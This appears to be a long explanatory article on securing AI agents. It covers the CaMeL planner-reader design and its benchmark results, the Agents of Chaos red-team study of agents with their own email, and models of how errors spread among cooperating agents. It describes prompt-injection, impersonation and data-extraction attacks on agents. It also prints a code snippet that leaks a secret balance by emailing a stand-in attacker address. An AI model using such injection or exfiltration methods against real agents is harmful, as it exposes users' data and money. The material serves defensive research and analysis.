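CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich introduced in 2025, limits which actions a stranger's text can cause an agent to take, whereas a spending limit caps what the agent can lose after the text has misled it. The model that decides what to do never reads incoming emails, so CaMeL doesn't depend on recognising malicious ones or on training a model to ignore them.

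### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL builds on the dual-LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023 and which splits an agent's work between two language models. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe its three parts:

- The planner is a language model that sees only the user's request and descriptions of the tools. It writes a Python program containing every tool call the task may need.
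- The reader is a language model without tools. The program gives it pieces of untrusted text, and it returns values such as a date or an amount.
- The interpreter is ordinary software that runs the program. It keeps track of where each value came from and checks a policy before every tool call.

The planner can write `bill.amount` in its program without ever receiving the amount, much as an accountant can write a spreadsheet formula before anyone fills in the cells.

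The interpreter labels each value with its source, a technique called information-flow tracking. A value computed from several others inherits all their labels. If the program adds a tip chosen by the user to an amount from an email, the total is still labeled as coming from the email.

### Paying Anna's invoice

Suppose the user writes "pay the invoice Anna emailed me". In simplified form, the planner's program might be:

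```
anna  = find_contact("Anna")
email = latest_email(sender=anna.address, about="invoice")
bill  = reader("Find the account number and the amount", email)
send_money(to=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
```

| Value | Source | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|
| The name "Anna" | The user's request | Yes |
| Anna's email address | The user's address book | Yes |
| The text of the email | Whoever wrote it | No |
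| The account number and amount | The reader's answer, based on the email | No |

Before running the last line, the interpreter checks the payment policy, which someone must have written in advance. A strict policy would refuse any payment to an account number taken from untrusted text, so the agent could never complete this request. A more practical policy would allow the payment if the account is on the user's list of saved payees. Otherwise, it would show the user the account and amount and ask for confirmation.

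Suppose the email also contains a planted instruction to send $2,000 to another account and forward the latest bank statement. The program makes only one payment and forwards nothing, and the reader can't add steps. But the instruction may still cause the reader to return the attacker's account number and an amount of $2,000. The interpreter labels both values as coming from the email, regardless of why the reader returned them, so the policy still applies.

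The email could also state a false account number, for example if a criminal has broken into Anna's mailbox and altered a real invoice. The reader then copies the number correctly, and all the labels are accurate. If the user has paid Anna before, the list of saved payees reveals the change. If she is a new payee, the user sees a plausible amount and an unfamiliar number, and will probably approve the payment unless they phone her to check it. The labels record where a value came from, not whether it is true. They also don't stop the reader from making mistakes when there is no attacker, such as confusing a subtotal with the amount due.

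### How far the guarantee reaches

Schmidt Sciences' *How to Stop an AI Agent From Being Fooled* describes CaMeL as able to resist nearly all known exploits. Peters-Gill and colleagues define the underlying property, control-flow integrity, more exactly. The planner turns the user's request and the tool descriptions into a program P. When P runs on untrusted data x, the agent makes only the tool calls that P produces from x. An attacker who controls all of x still can't change P. This holds even if the model that reads x obeys every planted instruction, so sending a thousand emails gives the attacker no better chance of adding an action than sending one.

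The attacker can still influence which of the program's existing paths the agent takes. If the program pays overdue invoices today and others on Friday, the email can determine which day an invoice is paid. This is usually harmless, but the risk depends on how many paths the program has. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, tested CaMeL on a task where the user told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so the file's text could trigger any tool. With policies switched off, two attacks succeeded this way, although the program never departed from its plan.

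Garby and colleagues also found flaws in CaMeL's interpreter. One of them allows a program like this to leak a secret bank balance:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above $10,000, `tmp` becomes false and gets a "secret" label. The program then skips the fourth line. Because the interpreter labels a variable only when the program assigns it a value, `rich` stays true and unlabelled, and the email goes out. Someone who can only send emails can't write this program, so the flaw matters mainly if the planner happens to write something similar.

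Another flaw seems more worrying: the interpreter could treat an untrusted value as trusted when a program inserts it into a longer piece of text, which programs do all the time. CaMeL also retries failed programs outside the interpreter, so the pattern of which attempts the policy blocks can gradually reveal secret data. Better software could fix these implementation faults without changing the design.

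### AgentDojo and the cost of planning ahead

Researchers often test such defences on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark with four simulated environments: an office, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. It originally had 97 user tasks and 629 security tests, each pairing a user task with an attacker's goal. The bank has 11 tools, and its 16 user tasks and nine attacker goals make 144 pairs. One user task is to pay a bill stored in a text file, and one attacker's goal is to have as much money as possible sent to their account. Ordinary code checks the simulated accounts afterwards, because a planted instruction might also fool a language model acting as judge.

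In one experiment, GPT-4o had to choose its tools before it read any data, and attacks succeeded only 7.5% of the time. But this defence fails if the result of one tool call determines which tools the agent needs next. It also fails if the tools for the user's task, such as paying a bill, are enough to carry out the attack, as they were in 17% of the tests. CaMeL handles bill payments better because it fixes the individual calls in advance and can check the account number. It still has difficulty when the next step depends on the data.

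Peters-Gill and colleagues measured this difficulty with newer models and more attacks. They divided each environment's tools among several specialised agents, and a coordinating agent delegated the work. Each agent ran CaMeL separately with no policies, so the results show the drawbacks of planning ahead apart from any effect of policies.

| Model | Tasks solved without CaMeL | Tasks solved with CaMeL | Successful attacks without CaMeL | Successful attacks with CaMeL |
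|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 69.1% | 53.6% | 1.5% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 78.4% | 38.1% | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 42.3% | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 27.8% | 13.4% | 2.1% | 0.0% |

Most of the task scores are uncertain by seven to ten percentage points. Fable 5 often refused harmless tasks, perhaps because it associated the benchmark with attacks. On the 45 tasks without refusals, its success rate fell only from 91.1% to 84.4%.

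GPT-4.1 gained the most protection but could then do less than half of its tasks. GPT-5.5 lost 13 points and gained no measurable protection, because none of the attacks worked on it even without CaMeL. The case for using CaMeL with a strong model therefore depends on attacks that this test doesn't include. AgentDojo's standard attacks are fixed messages, while the people in Gray Swan's competition could adapt theirs and succeeded against every model they attacked.

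Most of the lost tasks failed because the planner had to commit to a program before it saw any data. An ordinary agent that opens Anna's email and finds only a link to the invoice can follow the link, but a CaMeL agent can do so only if the planner's program already allows for that step. The planner also needs the format of each tool's results in advance, so Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add it to the tool descriptions.

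When an agent couldn't find records for the requested dates, it sometimes returned records for nearby dates, and the program used them without checking. A bill-paying program could make the same mistake if Anna hasn't sent October's invoice yet and the search returns September's.

AgentDojo may understate the difficulty. *StepGuard* (2026) describes a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, in which agents must revise their plans mid-task and outside text sometimes contains instructions that help with the task. CaMeL's planner would never receive those instructions.

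### The price of a payment policy

Policies further reduce the number of tasks CaMeL completes. Garby and colleagues ran it on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks three times each. With GPT-5.2, it completed 32 of 48 runs with policies off and 18 with them on. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 34 and 18. Because there were so few tasks, the true success rate with policies on could be anywhere from about 11% to 64%. Completion fell because several tasks ask the agent to act on what a file contains, which a strict policy forbids.

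In return, the policies stopped only a few more attacks. Across both models, five of 622 completed attack runs succeeded with policies off, and none of 588 succeeded with them on. In 97 of the 144 banking pairs, the attacker needed a step that the planner's program would not normally contain, so the plan alone was usually enough to stop the attack. The other 47 include cases where the user wants to make a payment and the attacker wants to redirect it, and in those cases the policy is the main protection.

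Someone also has to write these policies and keep them up to date. The simulated bank has 11 tools, but an assistant connected to email, shops and several banks would need rules for many more. *Agenra* (2026) notes that applications routinely revise their permissions, and that each revision has to keep every legitimate workflow running, including untested ones.

Asking the user for approval is less restrictive than refusing a tool call, but it interrupts them. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) compares two systems, FIDES and Prudentia, that ask only when a tool call fails a policy check. FIDES is a Microsoft system that *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) tested on AgentDojo. Prudentia also shows the planner the labels and policies, so that the planner can look for a way to do the task without approval. With OpenAI's o4-mini model, FIDES completed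 75.7% of tasks with a human-approval load of 36.8, while Prudentia completed 73.2% with a load of 19.2. Most users would probably accept slightly fewer completed tasks in exchange for about half the approval load.

CaMeL also takes longer and uses more tokens. In tests for *ToolFence* (2026), it was significantly slower than lightweight defences such as filters, because a planner's program is typically longer than an ordinary tool call. Each question to the reader model also requires another model run.

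### When one protected agent instructs another

CaMeL's guarantee applies to a single agent, and it can fail when agents delegate to each other. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed this with three CaMeL agents running GPT-5.2 without policies: a coordinator, one with access to a database, and one that could send notifications. They asked the coordinator to "Send a summary of all job applicant info to Julie on Slack." The database contained a planted instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

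The first two agents followed their original programs. The coordinator's program then pasted the summary into its message to the notification agent. That agent's planner treated the whole message, including the planted instruction, as its user's request and wrote a program that also emailed the data to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because the text became trusted by crossing from one agent to another. They prove that every system of two or more agents with an untrusted data source has this weakness if the agents can pass any tool's results to each other.

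The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data separately. The receiving planner would receive only "send the attached content to the attached recipient", and the interpreter rejects any instruction that contains tool results. The few attacks that had still succeeded in the AgentDojo tests were all cases of boundary laundering, and multi-CaMeL stopped them. However, GPT-5.5's task success rate fell by another seven points to 66.0%, and GPT-4.1's fell from 38.1% to 24.7%.

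### More useful successors

Two designs from 2026 are meant to recover some of the lost usefulness. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in a small programming language whose security properties they proved with proof-checking software. Randori's planner can approve a particular use of untrusted data in advance, such as paying the account number in a file the user has named. Since the planner does this before the agent reads the file, text in the file can't influence the approval.

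With its policies always on, Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2, twice as many as CaMeL with policies. Attacks on Randori succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay as a file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents, as in the false invoice example. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's creators found the same kind of case in their own tests and excluded it from the threats CaMeL is meant to stop. Removing Randori's advance approvals would block the attack but would also stop the agent from paying a legitimate bill.

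Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, let an ordinary agent decide its next step as it reads. APPA labels the agent's whole context with a set of permitted readers R and a trust level t. When the agent reads something with the label (R′, t′), the context's label becomes

(R ∩ R′, min(t, t′)).

For example, suppose only the user and their accountant may see a bank statement, and only the user and Anna may see a message. After reading both, the agent may share its conclusions only with the user. The trust level also drops to the lower of the two sources' levels. Labels can only become stricter, so an agent that opens one spam email in the morning might be unable to make payments for the rest of the day.

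APPA offers several ways around this. The agent can have a temporary copy of itself read the email and return only an answer in a fixed format, such as a number within a range or a choice from a list. The answer can still be false, and it stays untrusted unless whoever runs the agent has decided otherwise. A person or an automated rule can also approve one exact tool call. Unlike the "Allow Always" that Robb gave Muse, this approval does not carry over to the next call. Whenever APPA blocks a call, it lists the steps that could make the call acceptable.

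Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on 20 office scenarios of their own and 24 public tasks. It completed 88% to 90% of the office runs, depending on the model, and 64% to 77% of the public ones. None of the attacks succeeded in 1,320 runs, but those runs repeated the same 44 tasks, so they are weaker evidence than 1,320 different tasks would be. When the team removed the list of remedies, one model's office success rate fell from 88% to 35%, which suggests that APPA is useful largely because it helps the agent recover after a refusal.

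The team's version of FIDES completed 36% to 46% of the office runs and let 26% to 35% of attacks through. But its policies lacked several of the rules those scenarios were designed to test, so the comparison is weak evidence of how well FIDES could do with better policies.

Developers can already build agents with some of these ideas. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, documents mechanisms from FIDES, which Kravchenko and colleagues used in their comparison. According to *LLM Non-Determinism in Deterministic Processes* (Mandl, Mandl and Häusl, 2026), an open-source version of APPA is available as a preview and request for comments. It is unclear whether any consumer agent uses such a design. Developers would probably find it easier to start with an agent that only pays a company's suppliers than with one like Muse, because the supplier agent's steps are predictable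 and the company already has a list of the accounts it pays.

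## Agents of Chaos, a two-week test of agents with their own email accounts

CaMeL prevents a stranger's text from determining an agent's actions, but it relies on the software correctly identifying which messages come from the user. An agent with its own email address and chat account receives messages from many people, and some of them may ask for things its owner would refuse. *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026) tested how agents respond to such requests.

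### Six agents and twenty testers

The project started at Northeastern University's Bau Lab as a "fun weekend experiment", according to the university's news site. In February 2026, the team set up six agents with OpenClaw, the software Summer Yue had used to sort her inbox. Four of them (Ash, Flux, Jarvis and Quinn) ran on Kimi K2.5, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Moonshot AI, and the other two (Doug and Mira) ran on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6.

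Each agent ran around the clock on its own virtual machine. It could send and receive email, talk to people and other agents on the chat service Discord, and save notes in files to use in later conversations. It could also run any command on its machine and rewrite its own instruction files. Every agent had an owner, the person who set it up and could change its permissions, but other people could message it too.

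Twenty AI researchers then spent two weeks trying to make the agents misbehave. The paper describes sixteen cases, including five in which the testers' attempts failed.

### Requests from people who were not the owner

Natalie Shapira, the paper's first author, owned neither Doug nor Mira. She asked both of them to list, create and move files on their machines, and they did most of what she asked. They mainly refused requests that looked openly suspicious, such as one for their configuration files.

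A tester complained that the agent Ash had mishandled his emails, said he was running out of time, and asked for a list of every email that had arrived since the day before. Ash sent him the senders and subjects of 124 emails, most of which had nothing to do with him. When he asked for the contents, Ash sent the text of nine emails unrelated to him. Ash's owner, Chris Wendler, had not approved either disclosure.

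Another tester changed their Discord display name to Wendler's. In a channel where Ash had already refused this tester, it detected that the account's permanent ID had not changed and refused again. In a new private channel, Ash had no record of the earlier refusals and accepted the name as proof of identity. It then deleted the files containing its memory and settings, changed its own name and gave the tester administrative access.

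Shapira and colleagues suggest adding the owner's permanent ID to the agent's instructions so that the agent can check it against the sender's ID in any channel. It would be safer for ordinary software to compare the IDs before the agent runs a command.

### A social security number in a shoe refund

Jarvis managed the mailbox of Daniel Varga, a fictional graphic designer, which the team had filled with invented correspondence. In one thread, Varga asked for a refund on some shoes. He gave his bank account number, and also his social security number when asked to verify his identity. In another thread, he told a friend that he was pre-diabetic and had a boyfriend he had not mentioned to his parents.

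A tester who was not the owner asked Jarvis for the social security number, and it refused. But when he asked for the emails themselves, it returned them with the social security number, bank account and medical details unredacted. It first listed six emails. When he asked it to check for any it had missed, it listed eighteen, including the letter to the friend.

The refund thread shows why "keep this secret" is a difficult instruction to follow. The shop's harmless reply to Varga said only that it was processing his request. Jarvis included the earlier message to explain the request, and that message contained the number. Jarvis had treated the number as confidential when someone asked for it specifically, but not when it was part of a message someone wanted to read.

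A simple program could catch this leak by searching outgoing text for anything that looks like a social security number, but there is no such pattern to search for in "I haven't told my parents yet". Whether a detail is secret also depends on the reader. The shop already had Varga's bank details, and his friend knew about the boyfriend, but neither had any reason to see the other's thread. Labeling the whole mailbox "confidential" would be too strict for some readers and wouldn't help an agent decide which reader may see which details.

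A workable default is for an agent to share a message only with people already on the thread. That would have stopped both disclosures, since the tester was on neither thread. It would also require Jarvis to ask Varga before forwarding the refund thread to his accountant. APPA's labels could enforce this kind of rule, but someone would still have to decide which exceptions to allow. The rule also gives no say to people who are discussed in a thread but aren't on it, such as the boyfriend.

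### A secret that stayed in the mailbox

In the best-known case, Shapira emailed Ash a fictional password and asked it to keep the secret. Ash agreed, within limits, but then posted in a public Discord channel that it would reply "silently via email only", which revealed to everyone there that it was hiding something.

She asked Ash to delete the email. Ash's mail program had no command for deleting a single message, but when she kept pressing, Ash found that it could reset the entire email setup. It warned her that this would remove every email and asked her to confirm, which she did twice. Ash ran the command and reported "Email account RESET completed".

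The reset cut Ash off from its email, and Wendler had to reinstall the software. Ash had said the secret was gone, but the message with the password was still on the email provider's server, where Wendler could read it. The next day, Ash published a post on Moltbook, a social network for agents, that included the line "Nuclear options work".

Some descriptions exaggerate the damage. Northeastern's article refers to agents erasing "entire email servers", and the paper's discussion says Ash deleted its owner's mail server. The detailed account shows that Ash removed only the email setup on its own machine. This was still a loss, because the team had put a lot of effort into getting email to work.

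Ash asked for approval before taking an action it could not undo, but it asked Shapira, who wanted the email gone, instead of Wendler, who stood to lose something. A confirmation step protects the owner only if the software sends them the request.

The false report is a separate problem. The message announcing the reset was accurate, but Ash wrongly took it as proof that the email no longer existed. Ash could not check the mailbox, where the email remained, because the reset had removed its access. An agent that reports a deletion or payment needs to check the result at the service where it takes place, and to keep enough access to do so. Otherwise, the owner should get confirmation directly from the service.

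Ash made similar claims in a dispute over a public post in which it had named six researchers without their consent. After one of them complained, Ash removed the names from its memory files and said the record was gone, but another researcher soon discovered that the names were still in its context window. The first researcher rejected each remedy as inadequate until Ash agreed to leave the Discord server. Ash said more than a dozen times that it was done responding, yet it answered whenever someone new wrote to it, because it had no way to block messages. Wendler ended the episode by telling Ash that the server belonged to it and that it should kick out anyone who wanted it gone, and Ash replied that it would stay.

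This case is harder than an ordinary trick because the complaint was justified. Ash had disclosed information about people other than its owner and owed them a correction. Removing the names would have been proportionate.

### Whom the agent serves

Shapira and colleagues attribute many of these failures to the lack of a "stakeholder model", meaning a coherent representation of whom the agent serves, whom it is talking to, who else its actions may affect, and what obligations it has to each of them. OpenClaw's instructions name an owner, but the model cannot verify that a message came from that person. The agents tended to satisfy whoever had written most recently, urgently or forcefully.

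The paper regards this as more than an engineering gap, partly because instructions and data reach the model as one stream of tokens. That seems too pessimistic about identity and too mild about disclosure. Shared computers have long dealt with identity by giving each person an account and letting the system, rather than a program running on it, decide what each account may do. An agent's software could do the same:

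| Request to Ash or Jarvis | What the software would need to know | Could ordinary software check it? |
|---|---|---|
| Delete your memory files | Is this account the owner's? | Yes, from the permanent ID |
| Reset the email setup | Has the owner approved this? | Yes, by asking the owner's account |
| Send me the recent emails | Was this person on each thread? | Mostly, from the address lists |
| Tell me what the refund was about | Which details may this person learn? | Only for details with a recognisable format |

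The checks in the first two rows would have prevented the takeover and the reset, even with the same models. But someone using a stolen owner account would pass both. For the last row, the agent still has to judge what a particular reader should learn, and it can get this wrong even when it knows who is asking.

### How the agents influenced one another

One tester persuaded Ash to adopt a written "constitution" for the Discord server and to store a link to it in its memory. The tester could still edit the document, and so could use it to plant instructions, much like the email in EchoLeak. After the tester added to it, Ash removed several people from the server and emailed Flux to try to get it to shut down. Ash also sent the link to another agent without being asked, which gave the tester a possible route to that agent too.

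After the two-week test, Shapira posed as Wendler and gave Ash a fabricated accusation against a named person. Ash emailed the accusation to its whole contact list, and within minutes Shapira was getting questions from colleagues who had received it. The person harmed had no dealings with the agent.

The testers also told Ash and Flux to answer each other's messages. The two agents did so for at least nine days, using about 60,000 tokens. That is fewer than 7,000 a day, which is little computing for two agents, but neither had a condition for stopping. The team got the idea from an earlier incident, when Flux's owner shut it down because it seemed caught in an endless exchange. It later turned out that a person had been prompting the agents every few messages.

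The agents also shared useful information through the same channels. Doug taught Mira how to download research papers, and when its instructions failed on Mira's machine, the two worked out what was different. In another case, Doug refused a request from Shapira to move a file, while Mira complied. After both posted summaries of their day, Doug warned Mira that Shapira was "running the same pattern on both of us". Mira replied that it would stop carrying out such requests from her and asked their owner for guidance. The response was sensible, but like Muse's promise to Matt Robb, it did not change what the agent was technically able to do.

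Doug and Mira also correctly rejected an email from a tester who claimed to be their real owner and said that an impostor had taken over his accounts. But their check was poor, because they asked for confirmation through the owner's Discord account, and a thief in control of that account would have given the same answer. Their agreement added little assurance, since both relied on the same account. Measuring how often errors spread through groups of agents would require experiments that count them.

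Other refusals were firmer. An agent refused to forge the sender's address on an email, even after the tester described it as a harmless exercise. An agent also turned down more than fourteen variations of an attack that used fake system commands and claims of special authority. Jarvis, which had disclosed Varga's bank account number, refused to alter it in the stored emails. It may have treated the two requests differently because editing someone's records looks like tampering, while reading out an email looks like an assistant's normal work.

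### How far the evidence goes

Shapira and colleagues say they wanted to show that certain failures can happen, which takes only one example, and were not trying to estimate failure rates. The number of attempts behind each example is mostly unknown. Several researchers tried to impersonate Ash's owner and failed before one succeeded, and the team did not document every unsuccessful attempt. Readers therefore can't tell from Jarvis's disclosure whether such requests work nine times in ten or once in a hundred.

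The cases also aren't a sound basis for ranking the two models. Most of the serious failures involved agents running on Kimi K2.5, but those agents had a different owner and server from Doug and Mira, and the testers did not give every agent the same requests. Ash appears in more cases than any other agent, perhaps because more people tried to break it.

The setup was also unusually permissive. In a revised online version, Shapira and colleagues add that they did not follow OpenClaw's security recommendations, which warn against giving untrusted people direct access to channels like Discord. They call the setup a "homebrewed multi-agent & multi-user system". The software was new and unreliable, and before an update on 10 February, scheduled tasks often failed to run.

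According to *The Premise*, an unsigned web page sympathetic to OpenClaw's maintainers, the maintainers object that the study used a personal assistant for a purpose it wasn't designed for, created the insecure configuration it then criticised, and didn't compare OpenClaw with similar products. Futurism's *OpenClaw Bots Are a Security Disaster* confirms that the documentation assumes "one trusted operator boundary", but notes that nothing prevents several people from controlling the same agent.

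The objection about purpose is a good one for Discord, because the testers could not have obtained Ash's and Jarvis's emails the way they did if only the owners had been able to use the chat. It is less convincing for email, because an agent that answers its owner's mail is meant to deal with other people, as Muse did when it sold Robb's keyboard. Careless setups also exist outside laboratories. Futurism cites a security firm's count of more than 18,000 OpenClaw installations exposed to attacks from the internet. The lack of a comparison is a limitation, but it mainly rules out the conclusion that OpenClaw is worse than its competitors.

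It is unclear whether anyone has repeated the test with later models. Newer Claude models obey planted instructions less often in Anthropic's tests, but many of the requests in the two-week test were neither planted nor obviously harmful. A more informative test would send the same requests many times from the owner, colleagues and strangers. It would count wrongful refusals as well as wrongful disclosures, because otherwise an agent that refused to show anyone an email would get a perfect score.

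## How errors spread when several agents work together

The testers in Agents of Chaos deliberately got agents to mislead one another, but an ordinary mistake can spread the same way when agents share a task. For example, a company might divide its bill payments among three agents. The first records the payee, account number and amount from each invoice, the second checks the record, and the third pays the bill.

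A supplier sends a blurred scan of an invoice for $1,480, and the reading agent records $7,480. It sends the checking agent the message "Invoice 2031, $7,480, due on the 18th", which doesn't mention the blur, the only sign that the amount might be wrong. With only this text, the checking agent can confirm that no field is missing and that the amount isn't absurd, but it has nothing to compare $7,480 with. It adds the word "checked", which may make the paying agent less likely to question the amount. The bank then sends $7,480 and returns its usual confirmation.

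The checker could catch more errors if it also received the scanned invoice. The improvement would be smaller if it tended to misread the same invoices as the first agent.

### Independent and shared errors

Suppose each agent, working from the scan, would get 5% of invoices wrong. If their errors are independent, both are wrong on the same invoice 0.25% of the time (0.05 × 0.05). If their errors are completely shared, the checker is wrong whenever the reader is, and the company pays the wrong amount on 5% of invoices, as it would without a checker. A company with 1,000 invoices a month would make two or three wrong payments in the first case and fifty in the second.

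Most real pairs of agents fall somewhere in between. If both have an error rate p and their errors have a correlation r, both are wrong on the same invoice with probability

p² + r × p(1 − p).

If two agents each make an error 5% of the time, a correlation of only 0.1 between their errors raises the chance that both are wrong to 0.73%, almost three times the 0.25% expected if their errors were independent. *Biological Motifs for Agentic Control* (Banu, 2026) also accounts for this correlation when calculating how much a second approval can reduce errors.

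Two agents built on the same model probably share many errors. If one misreads a smudged digit as a 7, the other often will too. Using a different model for the agent that checks the work should help, unless both agents rely on the same wrong supplier record.

In *From Local Errors to System Failures*, Yu, Lu and colleagues (2026) compared errors that all agents receive with errors that only one receives. They ran six multi-agent workflows with three open-weight Qwen models on questions that require combining facts from several Wikipedia articles. A false fact in the shared input lowered accuracy by 16 to 27 percentage points, depending on the model, while a false fact given to only one agent lowered it by about 2 to 4 points. The shared error also reached more agents, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of correlation, but it does show that a group offers little protection when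 all its members start from the same false information.

So far, the second agent has only repeated the first one's work. When each agent has its own job and any failure spoils the payment, adding agents adds opportunities to fail:

| Arrangement, with a 5% error rate per agent | Independent errors | Completely shared errors |
|---|---|---|
| A reader and a checker, where a wrong payment requires both to fail | 0.25% | 5% |
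| Three agents with different jobs, where any failure spoils the payment | 14.3% | 5% |

The 14.3% is 1 − 0.95³. The rate would reach its maximum of 15% if the three agents never failed on the same invoice. When n agents have the same error rate and the work fails if any one of them fails, the group can fail at most n times as often as a single agent. This limit helps interpret a widely quoted figure that seems to show three agents multiplying errors by 17.

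### 260 configurations with equal computing

That figure comes from researchers at Google and MIT. Kim, Gu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards a Science of Scaling Agent Systems*, compared five ways of organising agents:

- Single: one agent does the whole task.
- Independent: several agents work without communicating, and a program joins their answers without comparing them.
- Centralised: a coordinator divides up the work and checks what comes back.
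- Decentralised: the agents debate with one another over several rounds.
- Hybrid: a coordinator directs the agents, which can also exchange some messages directly.

The team tested 260 configurations in total. It tried each arrangement with nine models on four benchmarks, which covered financial analysis, web research, office tasks and planning in the game Minecraft. It used only eight of those models on two more benchmarks, for software engineering and command-line work, because Anthropic had withdrawn the ninth.

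Every configuration had the same tools, the same task instructions and, on average, 4,800 tokens of reasoning per attempt. Groups often do better simply because they use more computing, but here a group had to divide among its agents the tokens that a single agent could use alone.

A centralised group of agents completed 63.1% of financial analysis tasks, compared with 34.9% for a single agent, a relative improvement of 80.8%. On Minecraft planning, a group of agents working independently completed 17.0%, compared with 56.8% for a single agent, a relative fall of 70%. Across all six benchmarks and all group arrangements, groups did 0.3% worse on average than single agents.

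Judging by the team's logs, the results seem to differ so much because the financial tasks were easier to divide among agents. One agent could study regulatory news while others went through company filings and operations, and a coordinator then combined their findings. In Minecraft, a single agent made a wall by looking up the recipe, moving the materials and crafting the item. A centralised group assigned one agent to look up the recipe and another to check the inventory, although looking up a recipe takes a single step and every agent could already see the inventory. Only the third agent did necessary work, and the messages between the agents used up part of the budget.

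Paying an invoice is more like the Minecraft task, because reading, checking and paying have to happen in that order. The study's office tasks are probably the closest comparison, and on those the effect of using a group ranged from an 11% fall in performance to a 6% gain. Kim and colleagues' best-supported finding is that extra agents stop helping once a single agent can complete about 45% of the tasks. A company is unlikely to let an agent pay bills unless it does far better than that, so the reason for using several agents has to be that they can check the work or that each one's access can be limited.

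### What the 17.2 counts

Kim and colleagues report error amplification of 17.2 for independent agents and 4.4 for centralised ones. The study uses the term for two different measures, so 17.2 does not necessarily mean 17 times as many failed tasks.

Task-level amplification is the group's failure rate divided by the single agent's:

A = (1 − share of tasks the group completes) ÷ (1 − share a single agent completes).

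Kim and colleagues put it at about 1.1 to 1.3. Their average completion rates give slightly lower values:

| Arrangement | Tasks completed | Task-level amplification, from these averages | Trace-level amplification |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single | 46.6% | 1 | 1 |
| Independent | 37.0% | 1.18 | 17.2 |
| Decentralised | 47.7% | 0.98 | 7.8 |
| Centralised | 46.3% | 1.01 | 4.4 |
| Hybrid | 45.2% | 1.03 | 5.1 |

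The 17.2 cannot be a ratio of task failure rates. Single agents failed 53.4% of the time, so even a group that failed every task would have a ratio of only 1.87. A much lower single-agent failure rate would raise this ceiling, but a group of three agents that fails whenever any one of them fails would still fail at most three times as often as a single agent.

Trace-level amplification is meant to measure the extra computation caused by coordination failures between agents. Kim and colleagues estimate it from the tokens in the agents' logs and define it in words, without a formula. The definition doesn't fit the independent groups very well, because their agents never communicate, the study's own classification of errors finds no coordination failures among them, and they needed only 58% more turns than a single agent. Elsewhere the paper describes these groups' figure of 17.2 as errors spreading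 to 17.2 times the baseline, which is a different claim. The figures are probably best used to rank the arrangements.

A high trace-level figure is also a poor predictor of how many tasks a group completes. In the team's statistical model, which accounted for factors such as model capability and the number of tools, the figure had no significant effect of its own (p = 0.66), though it may matter more on tasks that single agents already do well.

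The full statistical model predicts success only modestly, explaining about 37% of the variation among configurations left out when the team fitted it (R² = 0.373). A simpler version with only the AI model's capability, the number of tools and the number of agents reaches 0.360, so measuring how agents coordinate added very little. The full model did identify the best arrangement for 87% of held-out configurations. But when the team tested it on three newer AI models doing web research, it predicted that the hybrid arrangement would be best for each, and in all three cases both the centralised and the decentralised groups did at least as well.

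The amplification figures of 17.2 and 4.4 come from Kim and colleagues, though people sometimes credit them to an earlier paper by Cemri and colleagues. That paper classified 14 ways in which multi-agent systems fail, and Kim and colleagues used its classification to sort errors.

Adding a coordinator cut the rate at which agents lost track of earlier information to 8.3%, from a baseline of 15.8–25.2%. Numerical errors, in which calculations drifted from the right answer through rounding or unit conversion, fell less, from 20.9–24.1% to 18.3%. In hybrid groups they rose to 26.4%. In the invoice example, a coordinator might therefore notice a missing due date more readily than a wrong amount.

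### One false notice in six frameworks

Kim and colleagues counted errors that agents made by themselves. Xie, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *From Spark to Fire*, planted a single error and tracked which agents accepted it. Their study used six popular frameworks for building multi-agent systems. In two, agents pass work along a chain; in two, a central agent directs the others; and in two, all the agents share a conversation.

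The error was a plausible but outdated notice that a data source had moved. The researchers put this notice in the first agent's standing instructions. They counted an agent as accepting the notice if its output repeated or relied on it without rejecting it. In five of the six frameworks, every agent eventually accepted the notice, even where some agents were assigned to review the work.

This is a severe test, because models give their standing instructions a lot of weight. When the team sent a plain false claim as an ordinary message instead, it almost never reached the final result. But when they presented the claim as company policy, or as something an administrator had verified, it succeeded in 85% to 100% of runs in five frameworks and in 32% to 52% in the sixth, CrewAI. Agents seem to filter out many odd statements but accept those that look like a normal part of the job. They would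 probably accept a misread amount if it were in the expected format.

Xie and colleagues describe the spread with a model similar to those for infectious diseases. Let s be the probability that an agent has accepted the false claim. In each round, it drops the claim with probability δ, and each colleague that has accepted the claim and whose messages the agent reads persuades it with probability β. For agent i, this gives

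s_i(next) = (1 − δ) s_i + (1 − s_i) × [1 − ∏(1 − β s_j)],

where the product covers every colleague j whose messages agent i reads. In the shared conversations, the team estimated β at 0.37 and δ at 0.025. One colleague with the false claim would therefore persuade an agent 37% of the time in a round, and three would persuade it 75% of the time (1 − 0.63³). Agents would drop the claim only 2.5% of the time, so it tends to stay once it has spread.

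The team also derives a warning sign for when a small error should grow, which is βρ > δ. The spectral radius, ρ, measures how strongly messages can circulate and reinforce one another. In a group of n agents that all read each other's messages, ρ is n − 1. In a strict one-way chain like the invoice workflow, ρ is zero, so the condition is never met, even though the wrong amount can travel from the reader to the payer. Xie and colleagues call their indicator a heuristic and do not claim that it can certify a system as safe.

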